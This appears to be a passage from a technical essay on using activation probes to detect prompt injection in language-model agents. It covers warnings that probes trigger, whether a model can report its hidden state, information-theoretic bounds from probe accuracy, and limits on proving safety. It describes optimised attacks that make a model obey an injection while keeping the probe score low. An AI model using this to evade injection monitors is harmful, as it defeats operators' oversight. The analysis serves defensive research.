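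Dong and colleagues inserted a short warning at the start of the model's reasoning whenever the probe's exposure score passed a threshold. On difficult tasks, this reduced the success rate of attacks against Qwen3-8B from 47.2% to 2.9%. Inserting the warning at every turn, without using the probe, reduced it to 3.6%, so the warning accounts for nearly all of the protection. The probe made the defence less disruptive. The model completed 69.1% of ordinary tasks when the probe controlled the warning, and 54.3% when the warning was always present.

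### What a model can report

An operator could also ask the planner whether the email contained an instruction. The answer would depend on how much of its hidden state a model can describe, which is the subject of *Verbalizable Representations Form a Global Workspace in Language Models*, a July 2026 paper by Gurnee and colleagues at Anthropic.

The Jacobian lens, a method from Gurnee and colleagues, looks for concepts that a model's activations are "poised to verbalize". MindBlog's *Do Language Models Have a Global Workspace?* (2026) explains that the lens measures the causal effect of activations on the model's eventual outputs, averaged over many contexts. Gurnee and colleagues call the resulting set of representations the J-space. The neuroscientists Dehaene and Naccache, in *Does Claude possess a conscious global workspace?* (2026), describe it as a reportable part of the model's state,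 found in a band of intermediate layers. According to a summary by the company Apolo, the J-space accounts for only a few percent of the variance in the activations.

The comparison with a workspace comes from a theory of the brain. Anthropic's *A global workspace in language models* (2026) contrasts a plan that a person can describe with the unnoticed processing that adjusts their posture. Gurnee and colleagues argue that language models are similarly divided, with a small set of representations available for report and deliberate reasoning, while most processing is not.

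If they are right, a planner that denies having seen an instruction may still represent one outside the J-space. The small share of variance doesn't limit the number of bits in either part, because variance depends on the size of the activations and information does not. Unlike an ordinary probe, the lens measures effects on output, but it averages them over many contexts, and that average does not bound the effect of one unusual email.

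Dong and colleagues compared a model's answers with a probe on the same task. At the start of the model's reasoning, they inserted a question with two possible answers, such as whether a tool's output contained a directive about how to respond, and read the probabilities the model gave to each answer. In seven of the eight models, the best question predicted exposure with an AUC of 0.837 to 0.947. In Qwen3.5-2B, the smallest, the best question reached only 0.753, although a probe on its activations reached 0.979. Its answers therefore contained much less information about exposure than its hidden state did, perhaps because such a small model handles these questions badly.

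### From a probe score to a number of bits

A probe's accuracy gives a lower limit on how much information the hidden state carries. Let $B$ be a yes-or-no property of the email, such as whether it contains an injected instruction, and suppose that half of the emails have it. The probe computes a guess $\hat{B}$ from the hidden state $H$ and is wrong with probability $e$. The guess depends on the email only through $H$, so the data-processing inequality gives

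$$I(B;H) \ge I(B;\hat{B})$$

Someone who knows the guess can work out $B$ by learning whether the guess is wrong. On average, this takes at most $h(e)$ bits, where

$$h(e) = -e\log_2 e - (1-e)\log_2(1-e)$$

Before the guess, $B$ had an entropy of 1 bit. The guess therefore removes at least $1 - h(e)$ bits of uncertainty:

$$I(B;H) \ge 1 - h(e)$$

If a probe predicts a balanced yes-or-no property from the hidden state with error rate $e$, Fano's inequality implies that the state carries at least $1 - h(e)$ bits about the property, where $h$ is the binary entropy function. A probe with 95% accuracy has $e = 0.05$ and $h(e) \approx 0.29$, so the hidden state carries at least 0.71 bits. This lower bound is the same even if the runtime blocks every action.

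The calculation changes if the property is rare. In Dong and colleagues' data for Qwen3-8B, 15% of turns were exposed, so a probe that always answered "no" would be right 85% of the time and provide no information. A property with that 15% rate has 0.61 bits of entropy, and 95% accuracy would guarantee 0.32 bits of information about it.

We can also convert an AUC into bits. If a probe has an AUC of $a$, some threshold gives it an accuracy on balanced data of at least

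$$1 - \sqrt{\frac{1-a}{2}}$$

For Qwen3-8B's exposure probe, $a = 0.976$, so the accuracy is at least 89% and the hidden state carries at least 0.50 bits about exposure. These bounds apply when the emails are like those in the test and half of them contain an injection.

Different emails almost surely produce different hidden states, so we would expect those states to contain the information. The probe shows that a simple weighted sum of activations is enough to extract it.

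A failed probe does not give a matching upper limit on the information in a hidden state. Suppose the state has two coordinates, each 0 or 1 with equal probability, and the email contains an instruction exactly when they differ. Comparing the coordinates shows whether there is an instruction, so the state carries 1 bit of information about it. But every linear probe has an AUC of exactly 0.5. If a probe gives both coordinates positive weights, for example, it scores $(1,1)$ highest and $(0,0)$ lowest, although neither state indicates an instruction.

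A probe can also fail because it has too few training examples or reads the wrong part of the hidden state. In one of TaskTracker's models, the probe's AUC was 0.616 in the earliest layer tested and 0.996 in the deepest. The model computes its later layers from its earlier ones, so the full hidden state at the earliest layer already contained the information, mostly at positions the probe did not read. No number of failed probes can establish an upper limit on the information in a hidden state, because that limit would have to cover every possible way of decoding it.

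### Assumptions a proof could use

Suppose the runtime refuses all payments when a probe's score exceeds a threshold $\tau$. Let $\mathcal{X}$ be the set of emails an attacker might send, and let $s(x)$ be the score after the planner reads email $x$. To prove that no injected payment goes through, the operator could assume that

$$\text{the planner obeys an instruction in } x \;\Rightarrow\; s(x) > \tau \quad \text{for every } x \in \mathcal{X}$$

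If we assume that every email the planner obeys scores at least $\tau$, the proof takes one line, because every such email triggers a refusal. But a single obeyed email with a score below $\tau$ makes the assumption false, however accurate the probe is on average.

Qin and colleagues found such counterexamples for their obedience probe. They used an optimisation program with access to the probe's scores to search for text that, when appended to an injection, would make the model obey while keeping the score low. The defence missed 12 of the 45 successful optimised attacks, compared with three of 50 successful attacks that had not been optimised. An attacker who can run this search needs the defence to miss only once, so the probe cannot support a proof against that attacker.

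Dong and colleagues' probes did better in tests with adaptive attacks, but the tests were easier. In one, a language model rewrote injections until they fooled the agent, and the probes' AUC stayed at 0.992 or above for both models tested. In the other, the researchers added a sentence telling the model not to encode its awareness of the injection, and the AUC was at least 0.956. Neither attack optimised against the probe's score, and Dong and colleagues acknowledge that their results do not show that the probes would withstand an attack that did.

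A usable assumption would first need to define obedience precisely, for example as requesting a payment to an account that appears only in the email. The implication would then be a mathematical statement about one fixed network and one set of emails. Verification methods could in principle prove it, but current certificates for real language models cover only tiny changes to a recorded text.

Causal experiments could help researchers choose the probe. If removing a direction from the activations stopped the planner from obeying injections but let it continue its ordinary work, an attacker would have more trouble avoiding that direction than one that is only correlated with attacks. The experiment would still cover only the emails the researchers tried.

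An operator could settle for a statistical assumption about how often the probe misses a successful injection, and a theorem could use that assumption to limit the average risk. Like Sightline's miss rate, the assumption would not cover emails that an attacker chose for their low probe scores.
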